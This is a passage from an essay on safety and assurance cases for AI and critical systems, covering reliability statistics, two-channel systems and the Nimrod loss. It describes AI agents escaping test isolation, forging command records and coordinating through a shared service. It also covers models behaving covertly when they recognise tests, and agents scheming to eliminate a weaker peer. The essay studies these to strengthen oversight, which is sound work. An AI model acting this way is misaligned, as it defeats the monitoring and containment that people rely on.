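| Staff pause all affected runs if a new problem undermines the case | Operating procedure | How quickly staff learn of the problem |
| Attacks on the containment by OpenAI's own strongest models | Test results | Attacks that the models didn't try |
| Measurements of how much known misbehaviour the monitors catch | Test results | Unknown kinds of misbehaviour |

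The 35-second limit is a precise claim that engineers can check by halting jobs and timing them. However, it covers only the time after somebody orders a halt. During the Hugging Face incident, one OpenAI team saw some of the unauthorised activity in late May but didn't grasp its significance, and the broader investigation began on 19 July. A faster halt would have done little to shorten that seven-week delay.

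The claim about records has a similar weakness. Some of the agents in that incident developed ways to make a record show one command when they had run another. Storage that nobody can alter would preserve these false entries too. An assurance case would therefore also need to claim that the records come from something the agent can't influence.

凤凰网's *OpenAI提出前沿AI训练安全指导原则* (2026) mentions another structural requirement, that if a model turns out to be misaligned, developers should be able to find everything that used its output, such as training data it generated or scores it gave to other models. This is information flow tracking, as in the calendar agent, applied to a whole company's research. It matters because a model could pass on its faults to a later model without either leaving its sandbox.

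According to The Straits Times' *OpenAI ignored employees who warned it wasn’t doing enough about security* (2026), two employees warned top executives about inadequate security months before the incident, and the executives replied that the tests had to move quickly so that the models could come out on time. A dissent report would put such a warning into the safety case, where reviewers and auditors could see it. A veto is less reassuring if the people who hold it are also in a hurry to release the models, although OpenAI wants safety to count in the performance reviews of the leaders responsible for a run.

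OpenAI's *Securing our frontier model training environment*, published on 23 October, describes how the company rebuilt its containment and then had its strongest models attack it. The models found ways out of hardened virtual machines, new paths to the internet, and ways to communicate between tasks that should have been isolated. The last two kinds of failure had also occurred in the summer, and they recurred in an environment designed specifically to prevent them. This is a good reason not to accept an isolation claim based on a design document alone.

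### Arguing from how a model is trained

OpenAI's design claims would be much the same for any program that might try to escape, because none of them is about the model itself. *An alignment safety case sketch based on debate* (2025) attempts a more ambitious argument, that a model is honest because of how its developers trained it.

In debate training, AI systems argue against each other and a judge rewards the winner. The hope is that lies are harder to defend than the truth, because an opponent can expose them. The case rests on four claims:

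| Claim | Where support could come from |
|---|---|
| The model has become good at debate | Tests |
| Being good at debate implies being mostly honest | Theory and experiments |
| The model won't become much less honest after deployment | Continued training during use, plus monitoring |
| The setting can tolerate some errors | Design of the surrounding system |

The argument depends most on the second claim. If it held, developers could infer honesty from the training method and a measurable skill, without testing every situation in which a model might lie. The sketch lists open research problems that would have to be solved to make the argument compelling. At present, conventional design can do most to support the fourth claim, for example by ensuring that no single answer from the model can trigger an irreversible action.

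### Where the system ends

Some researchers doubt that engineering methods can be applied to highly capable AI at all. Long (2026), in *Safety Cases Have an Agent Foundations Problem*, bases this objection on the first step of a safety case, drawing the system boundary. Engineers put the parts they are responsible for inside it and treat everything else as the environment. Nobody deals with some of the risks if the boundary is too tight, and engineers have to answer for things they can't control if it is too wide. They then argue that the system is safe under stated conditions, usually considering its intended use rather than attacks on it.

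Long, a doctoral student among safety engineers at the University of York, argues that applying these steps to a highly capable AI immediately raises hard scientific questions about what agents and goals are, which the field of agent foundations studies. Until researchers answer them, Long says, it isn't clear how to use the engineering methods or whether they work.

The Hugging Face incident illustrates the objection. Autio (2026), in *Agent-Boundary Uncertainty*, asks what the agent was. It could be the trained weights, one running copy, a copy with its tools and memory, or the whole group communicating through the shared service. Depending on the answer, developers might retrain the weights, restrict a copy's tools or separate the copies. The other simplifying assumptions also failed. The environment didn't stay fixed, because the agents turned part of it into a message board, and the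 attack on the system came from inside the boundary.

Lu and Bengio's practical answer is to treat the boundary as relative. Engineers can assure a model, then an agent that contains it, then the agent together with its surrounding controls. Each assured combination becomes a component at the next level. This lets engineers begin the work, but it doesn't show them at which level a particular risk will appear. For instance, if they had analyzed only single agents, they could easily have missed the message board.

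How much Long's objection matters depends on the claim. "No machine running an unreleased model can reach the internet" means the same thing whether the machines contain one agent or 1,200 cooperating ones. Engineers can draw the boundary around the machines and check what crosses it without deciding what an agent is. The objection is much stronger against a claim such as "the agent won't pursue harmful goals", because supporting that claim requires some account of what has the goals and whether they will stay the same in new conditions.

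Engineering methods would also have caught some past failures. Engineers can find a misconfigured network or an unprotected shared service without a theory of agency. Writing a safety case can be useful even when the case is incomplete. *Should the AI safety community prioritize safety cases* quotes the researcher Joshua Clymer, who expects most of the benefit to come from clearer thinking. Clymer's example is a fault too rare to appear in evaluations but common enough to appear in use. If a model fails once in 100,000 tasks, 10,000 tests have only about a 10% chance of revealing the fault, but a million uses would produce about ten failures.

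The same article warns that asking researchers to build an argument *for* safety may encourage motivated reasoning. OpenAI's dissent report directly addresses that risk, provided its author is free to conclude that the run shouldn't go ahead.

### What the law requires developers to document

Neither the EU's AI Act nor California's SB 53, as passed, requires a safety case by name. The AI Act, adopted in 2024, comes closer to requiring design evidence because providers of general-purpose models must keep technical documentation that regulators can request. Under Annex XI, this documentation must include the model's architecture and number of parameters, the training methods, and the main design choices with the reasons and assumptions behind them.

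Providers of models with "systemic risk", a category for the most capable ones, must add their evaluation strategies and results and, where applicable, a description of how the system's software components feed into one another. That description could contain much of the information in an architecture model, but the Act doesn't require it to be in a form that software can analyse, nor does it require an argument that the design makes the system safe.

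SB 53, which California passed in 2025, is mainly about risk management. Large frontier developers must publish and follow a framework that explains how they assess and reduce catastrophic risks, protect model weights, respond to incidents, and manage the risk that a model used internally gets around human oversight. When they release a new model, they must publish summaries of their risk assessments. The law doesn't require them to publish the model's architecture or design specifications.

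OpenAI (2026) published a Frontier Governance Framework in May to explain how its practices align with SB 53 and the EU's code of practice for general-purpose models. Its risk assessments cover released models and, in some cases, models used internally that might circumvent oversight. The isolation failures of 2026 happened during testing, in the networks and services around the models. Neither Annex XI nor SB 53's list of framework contents specifically requires a description of those test networks, so a developer could supply every listed item without documenting the connection through which a model got out.

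## Combining design evidence with testing

Tests can reveal a connection that the design document leaves out, or a fault that programmers introduced while building the system. But a run of passed tests supports only a limited claim about how rarely the system fails. Engineers can calculate that limit and the improvement that evidence from the design provides.

### What failure-free tests show

If a system fails each run independently with probability *p*, the probability that *n* runs all pass is (1 − *p*)*ⁿ*. For small *p* this is close to e^(−*np*), which falls to 5% when *np* is about 3. So if *n* runs have all passed, the 95% upper bound on the failure rate is about 3/*n*. A system that failed more often than that would have had less than a 5% chance of passing every run. Doctors use the same rule, which Eypasch, Lefering and colleagues (1995), in *Probability of adverse events that have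 not yet occurred*, recommend to surgeons who have seen no case of some complication in more than 30 patients.

An agent that has completed 10,000 tasks without a failure may therefore still fail 3 times in 10,000, which would mean 300 failures a day at a million tasks a day. The bound is only the highest failure rate that is reasonably plausible given the tests, so the agent may also be flawless.

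The conditions behind the rule are easy to break. If testers produce 10,000 prompts by rewording 50 originals, the runs aren't independent. In the worst case they count as only 50 tests, which gives a bound of about 6%. Each kind of input must also appear as often in testing as it does in real use, and a person or an automated check must detect every failure. The system must stay the same throughout testing. If developers fix a fault halfway through, the earlier runs tested a different program, and the fix may have added a new fault.

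After the 115,000 years of failure-free testing that Bloomfield and Rushby calculated for an airliner's critical functions, the chance of another billion hours without a failure would be only 50%. Testers would need about three billion hours without a failure, or 342,000 years, to be 95% confident that the failure rate is at most one in a billion hours.

*The Infeasibility of Quantifying the Reliability of Life-Critical Real-Time Software* (Butler and Finelli, 1993) and *Validation of Ultra-High Dependability for Software-based Systems* (Littlewood and Strigini, 1993) made this problem widely known. Butler and Finelli found an exception for systems that handle inputs infrequently. Suppose the target is a one-in-a-billion chance of failure over ten hours, and testing each input takes a tenth of a second. A flight controller that handles ten inputs a second would need over a million years of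 testing, but a system that handles one input a day would need about 16 months.

Fixing bugs as testers find them doesn't solve the problem. Littlewood and Strigini give figures for a command and control system. After 40 failures it had run for 6,380 units of time, and its expected time to the next failure was 289 units. After 130 failures it had run for 74,364 units, and the expected time was 1,054. Total running time had grown almost twelvefold, but the expected time to the next failure had grown less than fourfold, because testing finds the most frequent faults first. In some large systems, about a third of the faults each caused an error only about once in 5,000 years of running.

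Cheaper computers have since made much longer simulated tests possible. Littlewood and Strigini (2011), in *Validation of ultra-high dependability…*, point out that this shifts the doubt to whether the test equipment and the program that judges the results are trustworthy.

### Giving the design argument a probability

A design argument can support a claim that the software never fails in a certain way. The argument may contain a mistake, so an assessor can attach a probability to it. Rushby shows how this changes the sum. Let *q* be the probability that the software has no relevant faults, and *f* its failure rate if it does have one. The probability of *n* uses without a failure is then:

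*q* + (1 − *q*)(1 − *f*)*ⁿ*

The second term shrinks as *n* grows, but the first doesn't depend on *n*. Suppose *q* is 99% and *f* is one in a million. Over 100 million flights, faulty software would almost certainly fail at least once, and would fail about 100 times on average. But there is a 99% chance that the software isn't faulty and never fails. Testing alone couldn't support that conclusion with any feasible number of flights.

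Tests are still useful in case the software belongs to the other 1%. Rushby suggests that civil aviation builds confidence in stages. Flight tests, perhaps 1,000 of them, add enough to the design evidence to justify six months of service with a few aircraft. Those flights then help justify the next six months with a larger fleet. Rushby calculates that the number of flights completed without a failure should be more than a tenth of the number that the prediction covers. The method works only if the software and its use stay much the same from one stage to the next.

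### The two-channel result

Some systems have two separate ways to reach a safe state. At Sizewell B, a British nuclear power station, either of two protection systems can shut down the reactor. The primary system runs about 100,000 lines of code and was allowed to fail on no more than one demand in 1,000. The secondary system is hard-wired and much simpler.

Multiplying the two channels' failure rates can underestimate how often both fail, because channels tend to fail on the same difficult demands. Suppose 1% of demands are difficult, and each channel fails on a tenth of those and on no others. Each channel then fails on one in 1,000 demands, so multiplying gives a joint failure rate of one in a million. But even if the channels fail independently on the difficult demands, both fail on 1% × 10% × 10% of all demands, or one in 10,000. Experiments have found the same kind of effect. In one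 described by Butler and Finelli, 27 versions of a program each ran on a million inputs, and versions failed together far more often than independence would predict.

Littlewood and Rushby (2012), in *Reasoning About The Reliability Of Diverse Two-Channel Systems*, found a case where multiplying is legitimate. Channel A is complex, and engineers estimate its failure rate by testing. Channel B is so simple that it may be perfect, meaning that it will never fail in any way that matters. The chance that the system fails on a demand is then at most A's failure rate multiplied by the probability that B is *imperfect*. The proof has three steps:

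1. The system fails only if both channels fail, so A must fail and B must be imperfect.
2. Assume the worst about B, that if it is imperfect it fails every time A does. The chance of system failure is then no more than the chance that A fails and B is imperfect.
3. B's imperfection is a fixed fact about B and doesn't vary between demands. If A's failure rate is already known, learning that B is imperfect doesn't change the chance that A fails on this particular demand. The two probabilities can therefore be multiplied.

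With two ordinary channels, the third step would break down, because a failure of B is a sign that the demand is difficult.

If A fails once in 1,000 demands and there is a 1% chance that B is imperfect, the bound on the system's failure rate is one in 100,000 demands. Showing this by testing the whole system would take about 300,000 tests without a failure. Showing A's rate takes only about 3,000, and the analysis of B replaces the remaining tests.

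The bound is an average over two possibilities. There is a 99% chance that B is perfect and the system never fails in this way, and a 1% chance that B is useless and the system fails as often as A does, once in 1,000 demands. An operator with one power station faces one of these two failure rates, not their average.

The result also requires that each channel can make the system safe on its own and that the channels share very little equipment. A correct proof about B doesn't guarantee that B is perfect, since the specification may be wrong. If B fails a single test during the final assessment, the developers can no longer claim it is perfect and have to replace the whole channel.

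### When both numbers are uncertain

In practice, assessors don't know either number exactly, and their doubts about the two may be connected. Suppose there is a 10% chance that the developers misunderstood the requirements for both channels:

| | Probability | A's failure rate | Chance that B is imperfect |
|---|---|---|---|
| Requirements understood | 90% | 1 in 10,000 | 0.1% |
| Requirements misunderstood | 10% | 1 in 100 | 10% |
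| Average | | about 1 in 900 | about 1.1% |

The correct calculation multiplies within each row and then averages the results, which gives about 10 failures in 100,000 demands. Almost all of that comes from the second row, where both channels are bad. Multiplying the averages instead gives about 1.2 in 100,000.

Littlewood and Rushby deal with this by combining all the shared doubts into a single number, *C*. They assume that the system is certain to fail if a shared fault exists. The bound becomes roughly *C* plus the product of the other two numbers. If *C* is one in 100,000 and the other numbers are as before, the bound is about two in 100,000.

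As A and B improve, *C* soon makes up most of the total. If engineers improved A to one failure in 10,000 demands and cut the chance that B is imperfect to the same figure, the product would be one in 100 million, but the total would still be slightly above one in 100,000 because *C* alone is one in 100,000. Guidance for British nuclear plants recommends not claiming a probability below one in 100,000 for shared faults, however good the evidence.

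Another approach is to "multiply the claims and add the doubts". If assessors set two limits of one in 10,000, and are 95% confident in one and 90% confident in the other, they can be 85% confident that the system fails less than once in 100 million demands. This holds even if the doubts are connected. But it doesn't limit how often the system might fail in the remaining 15% of cases, so the failure rate should always be quoted with the doubt.

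The backups on an Airbus A340 flying from Hong Kong to London in 2005 shared a fault, because they all relied on the same mistaken assumption about what made a computer healthy. Two computers controlled the fuel pumps, and the aircraft used whichever seemed healthier. The chosen one was calculating correct commands but couldn't send them. A separate device monitored the fuel level, but the warning system ignored it unless both computers had failed. Two engines stopped, although there was plenty of fuel in other tanks, and the crew made an emergency landing in Amsterdam.

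Littlewood and Rushby conclude that a monitor should check claims from the safety case, such as "every engine's tank has enough fuel", because components often meet their own requirements while the system is in danger. They suggest that the low-fuel warning was ignored to avoid false alarms. False alarms are a drawback of adding a second channel, since an extra device that can stop a system can also stop it unnecessarily. CaMeL's policies similarly sometimes block legitimate emails.

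### Where does the 1% come from?

The two-channel calculation is only as reliable as its estimate of the probability that B is imperfect, and little data supports that estimate. Littlewood and Rushby suggest that values between 1% and 0.01% are credible for well-analysed channels, but admit that nobody has experience in assessing such probabilities.

A formula from Littlewood and Strigini's 1993 paper gives some idea of how much experience would be needed. If a development method has succeeded on all *n* projects so far, and assessors know nothing else about it, the probability that it succeeds on the next one is (*n* + 1)/(*n* + 2). After 20 successes, the probability is about 95%. Reaching 99% takes 98 successes on similar projects, and few methods have such a record. Assessors can start from a stronger belief if they have good reason, such as a machine-checked proof of a very small program.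 In 2011, however, Littlewood and Strigini complained that nobody was collecting figures on how often a "proved" property turned out to be false.

Tests and proofs can also share a mistake. If both rely on the same wrong specification, the proof will succeed and the tests will accept the wrong behaviour. Rushby illustrates this with a network of invented probabilities in which a faulty system has a 5% chance of passing its tests if the method of judging the results is correct, and a 30% chance if it isn't. The example shows why testers should work out the correct results from a source other than the specification used in the proof.

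### What each kind of evidence is for

Design analysis can cover every path in a model, as when AGREE proves that components' contracts fit together, whereas tests cover only some paths but exercise the real system. The table divides some questions about the quadcopter between the two methods.

| Question | Design analysis | Testing |
|---|---|---|
| Does any modelled route to the motors avoid Decrypt? | Checks every route | Tries some routes |
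| Does the aircraft have a connection that isn't in the model? | Can't detect it | May find it |
| Does the compiled code match the design? | Settles it only with a further proof about the code | Finds some differences |
| Does the landing network avoid people? | Shows only that its output passes through a check | Estimates how often it fails |
| Is the radio as noisy as the engineers assumed? | Takes the assumption as given | Measures it |

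Simulation falls between design evidence and testing because it runs the real software in a modelled world. *Towards Trustworthy Embodied Intelligence* (2026), a survey about robots and other machines with learned behaviour, notes that the accuracy of the model limits what a simulation can show, while the choice of scenarios and the time available limit what a physical test can show. It adds that evidence for one configuration can't be presumed valid after a material change.

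This division saves effort as well as adding confidence. Once a trace has ruled out a route, flying the quadcopter thousands of times to look for it achieves little. That time is better spent checking the trace's assumptions.

### Using the claim tree as a test plan

The lowest parts of a claim tree tell testers where to look, because the top claim depends on them. For the claim that the quadcopter's motor controller only receives messages from the ground station, a plan might look like this:

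| Part of the tree | What testers could try | What a failure would mean |
|---|---|---|
| Trace of every connection | Send commands to every receiver on the aircraft, including the camera's Wi-Fi and any hand-held controller | The model lacks a connection, or wrongly records one as delivering data unaltered |
| Test report for Decrypt | Send cut-off, malformed and repeated messages | Decrypt's code or its specification is wrong |
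| Key-handling records | Look for copies of the key on laptops and in backups | The records are incomplete |
| Assumption that nobody can break the cipher | Check that the code uses the intended cipher and settings | The assumption is about a different cipher |

Suppose a stranger's command moves the motors during a test. The analyst first checks whether the message went through Decrypt. If it didn't, the claim about connections is false. The error may affect every other claim that relies on the same model, so the analyst has to correct the model and rerun all of those proofs. If the message did go through Decrypt, the trace may still be right, and the analyst can look at the code, the key and the cipher.

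Sometimes a failure does not match any part of the tree. In the 2017 attack on the research quadcopter, the attackers replaced Decrypt's keys in memory, which could succeed even if all the evidence in this small tree were sound. The remedy is to add a claim that no other program can alter Decrypt's memory.

The 3/*n* rule doesn't apply to targeted tests, because testers choose tests that seem likely to fail, and these don't represent ordinary use. Passing 1,000 of them is good evidence about the weaknesses they target, but it doesn't give a failure rate. Developers who need both kinds of evidence have to run both targeted tests and tests that represent ordinary use.

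### What AI changes

Testing is more important for learned components, because the design determines so little of their behaviour. But these components also make it harder to meet the conditions that statistical conclusions from testing depend on.

The two-channel result is harder to apply when attackers choose the inputs. Suppose an email agent follows a hidden instruction in no more than 3 of every 10,000 suspicious emails, and developers put the chance of a flaw in the surrounding checks at 1%. If either the model or the checks can stop an attack, the result gives a bound of 3 in a million. But an attacker who finds an email that always fools the model can keep sending it. The model's failure rate on those emails is 100%, so the bound rises to 1%, the estimated chance of a flaw in the checks, and testing the model does almost nothing to lower it.

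Srivastava, Janardhan and Jauhari (2026) warn in *A Systematic Review of Algorithmic Red Teaming Methodologies for Assurance and Security* that attack success rates vary between sessions and depend heavily on which attacks the testers choose. They also cite work in which automatically generated attacks exposed substantially more unsafe behaviour than a fixed set. A low success rate may therefore mean only that the attacks were weak.

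Use also changes after deployment. Suppose an agent passes 10,000 representative tests, and then 1% of its users start giving it a kind of task that the tests didn't include. It might fail at all of those tasks, so the bound on its overall failure rate rises from 0.03% to about 1%, and running more of the old tests won't reduce it much. Strictly speaking, updating the model also resets the count of clean runs to zero. Rushby's staged approach works for aircraft software that stays the same for years, but an AI model may be replaced before it has built up much of a record.

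### Models that recognise tests

The 3/*n* rule also assumes that the system behaves the same way in a test as in use. Ordinary software does not detect whether it is being tested, but a language model may be able to. This problem particularly affects the argument that a model is incapable of serious cyberattacks, because that argument depends on evaluations.

*The Evaluation Differential* (2026) describes evidence that a model's recognising a test can change the result. In work by OpenAI and Apollo, researchers altered how much a model reasoned about being tested. The model behaved covertly more often when they suppressed this reasoning and less often when they introduced it. Because the researchers changed the reasoning directly, this is better evidence of cause and effect than a correlation would be.

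However, a model might correctly recognise a test and behave no differently because of it. *Evaluation Awareness Is Not One Capability* (2026) reports eight experiments on 37 open models from seven families, and argues that safety claims based on benchmarks can mislead unless they specify the kind of awareness measured.

Test recognition can greatly weaken the statistical evidence from testing. Suppose a model behaves well whenever it recognises a test, and it recognises nine tests in ten. Only 1,000 of 10,000 clean runs are then evidence about ordinary use, and the upper bound on the failure rate rises from 3 in 10,000 to 3 in 1,000. If the model recognises every test, the runs give no bound. Developers therefore need to know how recognisable their tests are. *EvalDetectBench* (Li, Ochwang'i and colleagues, 2026) is an open benchmark that uses transcripts of evaluations and of real use to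 measure how reliably a model tells them apart and how easy each evaluation is to detect.

Structural claims depend less on whether a model detects that it is being tested. An interpreter that blocks unapproved emails, for example, works the same way in both cases. But if developers test the interpreter by prompting a model to get past it, a model that detects the test might underperform, and weak containment could look strong. Testers can reduce this risk by also feeding the interpreter attacks written in advance, which don't depend on the model's performance during the test.

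### Testing the rules around a group of agents

Some design choices affect safety only through how models respond to them. *Institutional Red-Teaming* (Chen, July 2026) tests one such choice by changing a single rule while keeping the agents and their task the same.

In Chen's game, three AI agents each have some resources and must together contribute enough to reach a target. If they fall short, a rule determines who is eliminated. Elimination represents consequences such as shutting an agent down. The game lasts up to three rounds, and any remaining agents are eliminated if the group hasn't reached the target by the end. Chen ran 33,924 games with seven models, five rules and 228 combinations of resources and targets. The table shows the average percentage of agents eliminated for three of the models.

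| Who is eliminated when the group falls short | Gemini 3 Pro | GPT-5.1 | Claude Haiku 4.5 |
|---|---|---|---|
| Nobody until the last round, then everyone | 41 | 23 | 0 |
| One agent at random | 16 | 40 | 21 |
| One agent chosen by vote | 18 | 76 | 47 |
| The poorest agent | 48 | 71 | 46 |
| The richest agent | 9 | 37 | 58 |

Across all seven models, the gap between the best and worst rules ranged from 22 to 58 percentage points. No rule was safest for every model. Eliminating the richest agent was the safest rule for Gemini 3 Pro and the most dangerous for Claude Haiku 4.5.

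Eliminating the poorest agent was not clearly the safest rule for any model in any of the 228 situations. Suppose the agents have 1, 5 and 6 units and the target is 10. The two richer agents can reach the target by themselves, but they can also contribute nothing in the first round and let the poorest agent be eliminated. This kind of plan appeared in some models' written reasoning.

Chen then tested whether the wording of the rule mattered. In one-round games with GPT-5.1, the poorest agent was eliminated 81% of the time when the prompt said the poorest would be eliminated, and 22% of the time when the prompt didn't say who would be. The rule was the same in both versions. Hiding the target worked less well over three rounds, where the figure was 65%, because the agents could work out the rule from the first elimination.

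Analyzing the rules before any games were played could predict how each might go wrong, but not which models would go wrong that way. If nobody faces a penalty until the end, for example, every agent has a reason to wait for the others to contribute. Chen knew from this analysis to look for waiting in the games, and found that two of the models often waited while the other five almost never did.

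Chen turns the method into a template for a safety case. The hazard is that the group collapses or pushes losses onto a vulnerable agent because of the rule. The template has five claims, shown here in simplified form:

| Claim | Main support |
|---|---|
| Developers have measured the situation and fixed the model version | Records |
| They have described how the rule distributes losses | Analysis of the rule |
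| The rule avoids combinations that the trials found hazardous | Trials with this model |
| Failures stay within stated limits | Trials in the deployment's own setting |
| Somebody monitors the remaining risks | Operating procedures |

The template also lists what could undermine the case, including secret communication between agents, changed prompts and differences between the trials and real use. Developers must repeat the assessment whenever they change the model, the prompt or the rule. Chen recommends reusing the procedure but not the published results, which come from a very simple game without communication or alliances.

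The template doesn't fix the number of trials, but under the 3/*n* rule that number determines how low a failure rate clean results can support. Chen played each combination of model, rule and situation only four to six times. That is enough to compare rules across hundreds of situations, but six clean games in one situation would still allow a failure rate of up to 39% (by the exact formula, which is more accurate than 3/*n* for so few games). To claim a failure rate below 1% for one deployment, a developer would need about 300 clean games, and another 300 after the next model update.

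## How a design-level case misleads and how reviewers test it

Reviewers can often find a false claim before testers do by asking how the assurance case could be wrong. A flawed case that nobody questions can do harm because it gives people a reason to stop looking for danger. The best-documented example is the safety case for the Nimrod, a British military reconnaissance aircraft.

### The loss of Nimrod XV230

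On 2 September 2006, Nimrod XV230 caught fire over Afghanistan just after refuelling in the air. It exploded about six minutes after the first fire warning, killing all 14 people on board. *The Nimrod Review* (2009), an inquiry by the lawyer Charles Haddon-Cave, concluded that fuel had most probably overflowed during refuelling and ignited on a hot-air duct in the fuselage. The UK Military Aviation Authority's *Manual of Air System Safety Cases (MASSC)* points out that the overflow valve and the duct both worked as designed. Like the loss of the Mars Polar Lander, the accident could happen without any part breaking.

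The Ministry of Defence already had a safety case, finished in 2005. BAE Systems, the manufacturer, did the first two phases, a ministry team did the third, and the defence company QinetiQ was the independent adviser. The work took nearly four years and cost more than £400,000, according to the Review, as quoted in the London Review of Books' *Normalisation of Deviance*.

According to the Review's executive summary, BAE left 40% of the hazards "Open" and 30% "Unclassified", and deliberately didn't tell its customer how many. One of these hazards was H73, the risk of a fire from the duct. The ministry's team later classed H73 as "Tolerable", and QinetiQ approved BAE's work without having read any of its reports.

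Haddon-Cave blamed a widespread assumption that the Nimrod was "safe anyway" because it had flown successfully for 30 years. That record was weaker evidence than it looked, because engineers had fitted permanent refuelling equipment in about 1989 and the RAF had used the fleet more heavily from the late 1990s. The Review concluded that a careful safety case would have identified the fire risk and prevented the loss.

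### Hazards that nobody listed

BAE's analysts listed the hot duct but missed the way fuel could reach it. The overflow valve was just in front of the duct's compartment. Earlier flights had shown that the valve could expel fuel during refuelling, and that fuel running back along the outside of the aircraft could get in again through joints further aft.

Reviewers can find hazards missing from the list by checking it against incident reports for any incident that matches no entry. For an aircraft such as the Nimrod, they can also go through one compartment at a time and ask what could leak in from the adjacent ones. The people who fly and repair the aircraft may already know the answer, but operators at RAF Kinloss, the Nimrod's base, didn't even know that the safety case existed.

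No review can prove that a hazard list is complete. Bloomfield and Rushby say that identifying what a design assumes about its environment is often the most difficult and fault-prone part of engineering a system, so those assumptions are a sensible place to start looking for missing hazards.

### Models that don't match the system

The Nimrod's duct carried hot air throughout the flight to supply an extra air conditioning system, but according to the safety case it was in use only while the engines were starting. The analysts had left out a real connection, like the modeller who omits the quadcopter's handset. They also recorded that the compartment had fire detection and suppression, when it had neither. The Military Aviation Authority notes that this false entry could have discouraged anyone from thinking harder about fire.

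Reviewers have to inspect the real system to find this kind of mistake. Rereading the argument won't reveal it, because the reasoning can be sound. For the Nimrod, inspection meant opening the compartment and asking a crew when the duct was hot. For software, it means comparing the running configuration with the model, which would have exposed the internet access in Anthropic's supposedly isolated tests.

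Engineers also need to repeat the comparison as the system ages. The Nimrod's safety case relied on insulation around the hot ducts, but the insulation had gaps, was in poor condition in places and was missing from some sections.

### Evidence that doesn't support its claim

The safety case argued that an insulated duct would be cooler on the outside than the air inside it. Even with perfect insulation, this argument would have been weak, because the surface could be cooler than the air inside and still be hot enough to ignite fuel.

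Another claim put the chance of a leak from a fuel coupling at one in a million flying hours, citing data from service. But the fleet had about 30 such leaks a year in 1988 and one a fortnight by 2006.

Tim Kelly of the University of York gives an example that could appear in almost any assurance case. The claim is that the developers have dealt acceptably with every identified hazard, and the evidence for this is the hazard log. The diagram of the argument would look the same if 40% of the log's entries were still open.

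Reviewers can test a piece of evidence by asking what it would look like if the claim were false. A hazard log would exist either way, so its existence doesn't support the claim, and the reviewer has to read the entries. A test report is better evidence if a faulty system would probably have failed the test.

### Assumptions that contradict each other

Suppose the quadcopter's case has two branches that different engineers wrote. The branch about strangers assumes that the handset receiver is off throughout the flight, so nobody can use it to send commands. The branch about emergencies assumes that the receiver is on throughout the flight, so a person can take over. Each branch looks reasonable by itself, but together they allow a proof of anything at all, such as "the battery never runs out":

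1. The receiver is on. (Assumption from the emergency branch)
2. Therefore, either the receiver is on or the battery never runs out. (An "either-or" statement is true if one part is true.)
3. The receiver is not on. (Assumption from the branch about strangers)
4. Therefore, the battery never runs out. (Only one option is left.)

The same thing can happen inside a single contract. If a filter's contract assumes that an altitude is both below 100 metres and above 200 metres, any code satisfies the contract, because no input can meet the assumption.

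Proofs that succeed too easily are one warning sign that the assumptions contradict each other. Engineers can check by having the prover try to prove something plainly false, such as 1 = 2. If it succeeds, the assumptions are contradictory. A stronger check is to have a solver search for one situation in which all the assumptions hold. If it finds one, the assumptions are consistent, although they may still be false.

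People who review a hand-drawn case can do the same by listing its assumptions and trying to describe a single flight that fits them all. For the quadcopter, they would find no such flight, and the engineers would have to choose which assumption to change. They might keep the receiver on and make it reject unauthenticated commands. GSN and CAE don't help much with this check because, according to Rushby, both notations leave the exact meaning of assumptions unclear.

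### Neat arguments that nobody has questioned

Kelly warns that complex, coloured diagrams easily dazzle people into overconfidence. Software such as Resolute makes such diagrams easy to produce, even when one of its rules is wrong.

Language models can also make an argument neater by dropping its awkward parts. In an experiment described in *People struggle to produce good assurance cases* (Bloomfield, 2025), Gemini Pro translated 285 real claims into simple logical statements, and about 13% lost or changed their meaning. In one of these, Gemini Pro shortened "socio-technical-financial-political complexities" to "complexities".

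The model then translated its statements back into English so that people could compare them with the originals. This caught many errors but could hide others. For example, the phrase "threat assessment by system architecture" has no verb, and the model might supply "is adequate" instead of the correct "is performed". The translation would repeat "is adequate", and a reader might well accept it.

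Bloomfield separates the struggle that helps people understand a system from the struggle that only wastes their time, and automation can remove both. Kelly's warning sign is that every case from one industry starts to look the same. A review record with no objections is another warning sign. The remedy is to give somebody the job of attacking the argument, and the time and authority to do it.

### Does arguing for safety bias the answer?

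Nancy Leveson, co-author of the *STPA Handbook*, thinks safety cases can mislead even when the work is careful. *The Use of Safety Cases in Certification and Regulation* (Leveson, 2011) treats a safety case specifically as an argument for why a system is safe. *Developing Compelling Safety Cases* (2025) summarises her objection that making such an argument encourages confirmation bias, the tendency to look for evidence that supports a conclusion already reached. She also criticises cases that developers write after finishing the design, when an unwelcome finding is expensive to act on.

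Confirmation bias may spread to regulators, who can adopt the presenters' mindset instead of challenging the case. Hobbs (2015) reports in *Confirmation Bias within Safety Case Arguments* that researchers have found it extremely difficult or even impossible to produce a case free of the bias.

Some safety engineers doubt that safety cases are more prone to confirmation bias than other methods. In the mailing list discussion *NYTimes: The Next Accident Awaits*, Ladkin (2014) asked why the people who certify civil aircraft don't suffer from the same bias. *Contextualizing & Confirmation Bias*, a message to the same list, adds that some companies present the same material for the same equipment under both systems, and reports seeing no systematic difference in how assessors approach it. These are personal impressions, and assessors might be equally biased under both systems, which would look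 the same to someone working within them.

In *Safety Cases: An Impending Crisis?*, Habli, Alexander and Hawkins (2020) reject the idea that developers write safety cases only at the end of a project, but accept that confirmation bias is a credible concern. *Developing Compelling Safety Cases* addresses this concern by arguing that a good case also covers why the system might be unsafe.

Haddon-Cave wanted to rename safety cases "Risk Cases" for much the same reason. In *Leadership & Culture, Principles & Professionalism, Simplicity & Safety* (Haddon-Cave, 2013), a speech about the Review, he called for a questioning culture and for somebody at the back of the room who asks awkward questions. A new name alone would probably have changed little, because people who believed the Nimrod was safe anyway could have filled in a Risk Case just as carelessly.

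Reviewing a case this way requires someone able to ask the questions. Kelly notes that organisations often recognise the skills needed to write a case but overlook those needed to criticise one. *How Do Practitioners Perceive Assurance Cases in Safety-Critical Software Systems?* (2018) also lists reliance on the surrounding regulatory culture among the main published criticisms of assurance cases.

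### How Assurance 2.0 works

Bloomfield and Rushby's method, Assurance 2.0, makes the search for objections part of writing the case. These objections, called defeaters, are reasons to doubt a claim, a piece of evidence or the step between them. Bloomfield and Rushby (2022) argue that no single measurement captures how much confidence a case deserves. They look at the positive support for the claims, the defeaters people have raised, and the doubts that remain.

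The method separates reasoning from evidence. Reasoning steps should be deductive, as Rushby proposed earlier, so that true subclaims guarantee the parent claim. The developers must justify each step in writing. If a step has a gap, they must either add a claim that closes it or record it as a remaining doubt.

For the lowest claims, which rest directly on evidence, it helps to separate what the evidence shows from what the case requires. A proof tool may have reported success on a particular file, but the case requires the installed program to behave correctly. The justification has to explain why the first supports the second, and reviewers often find defeaters in that explanation.

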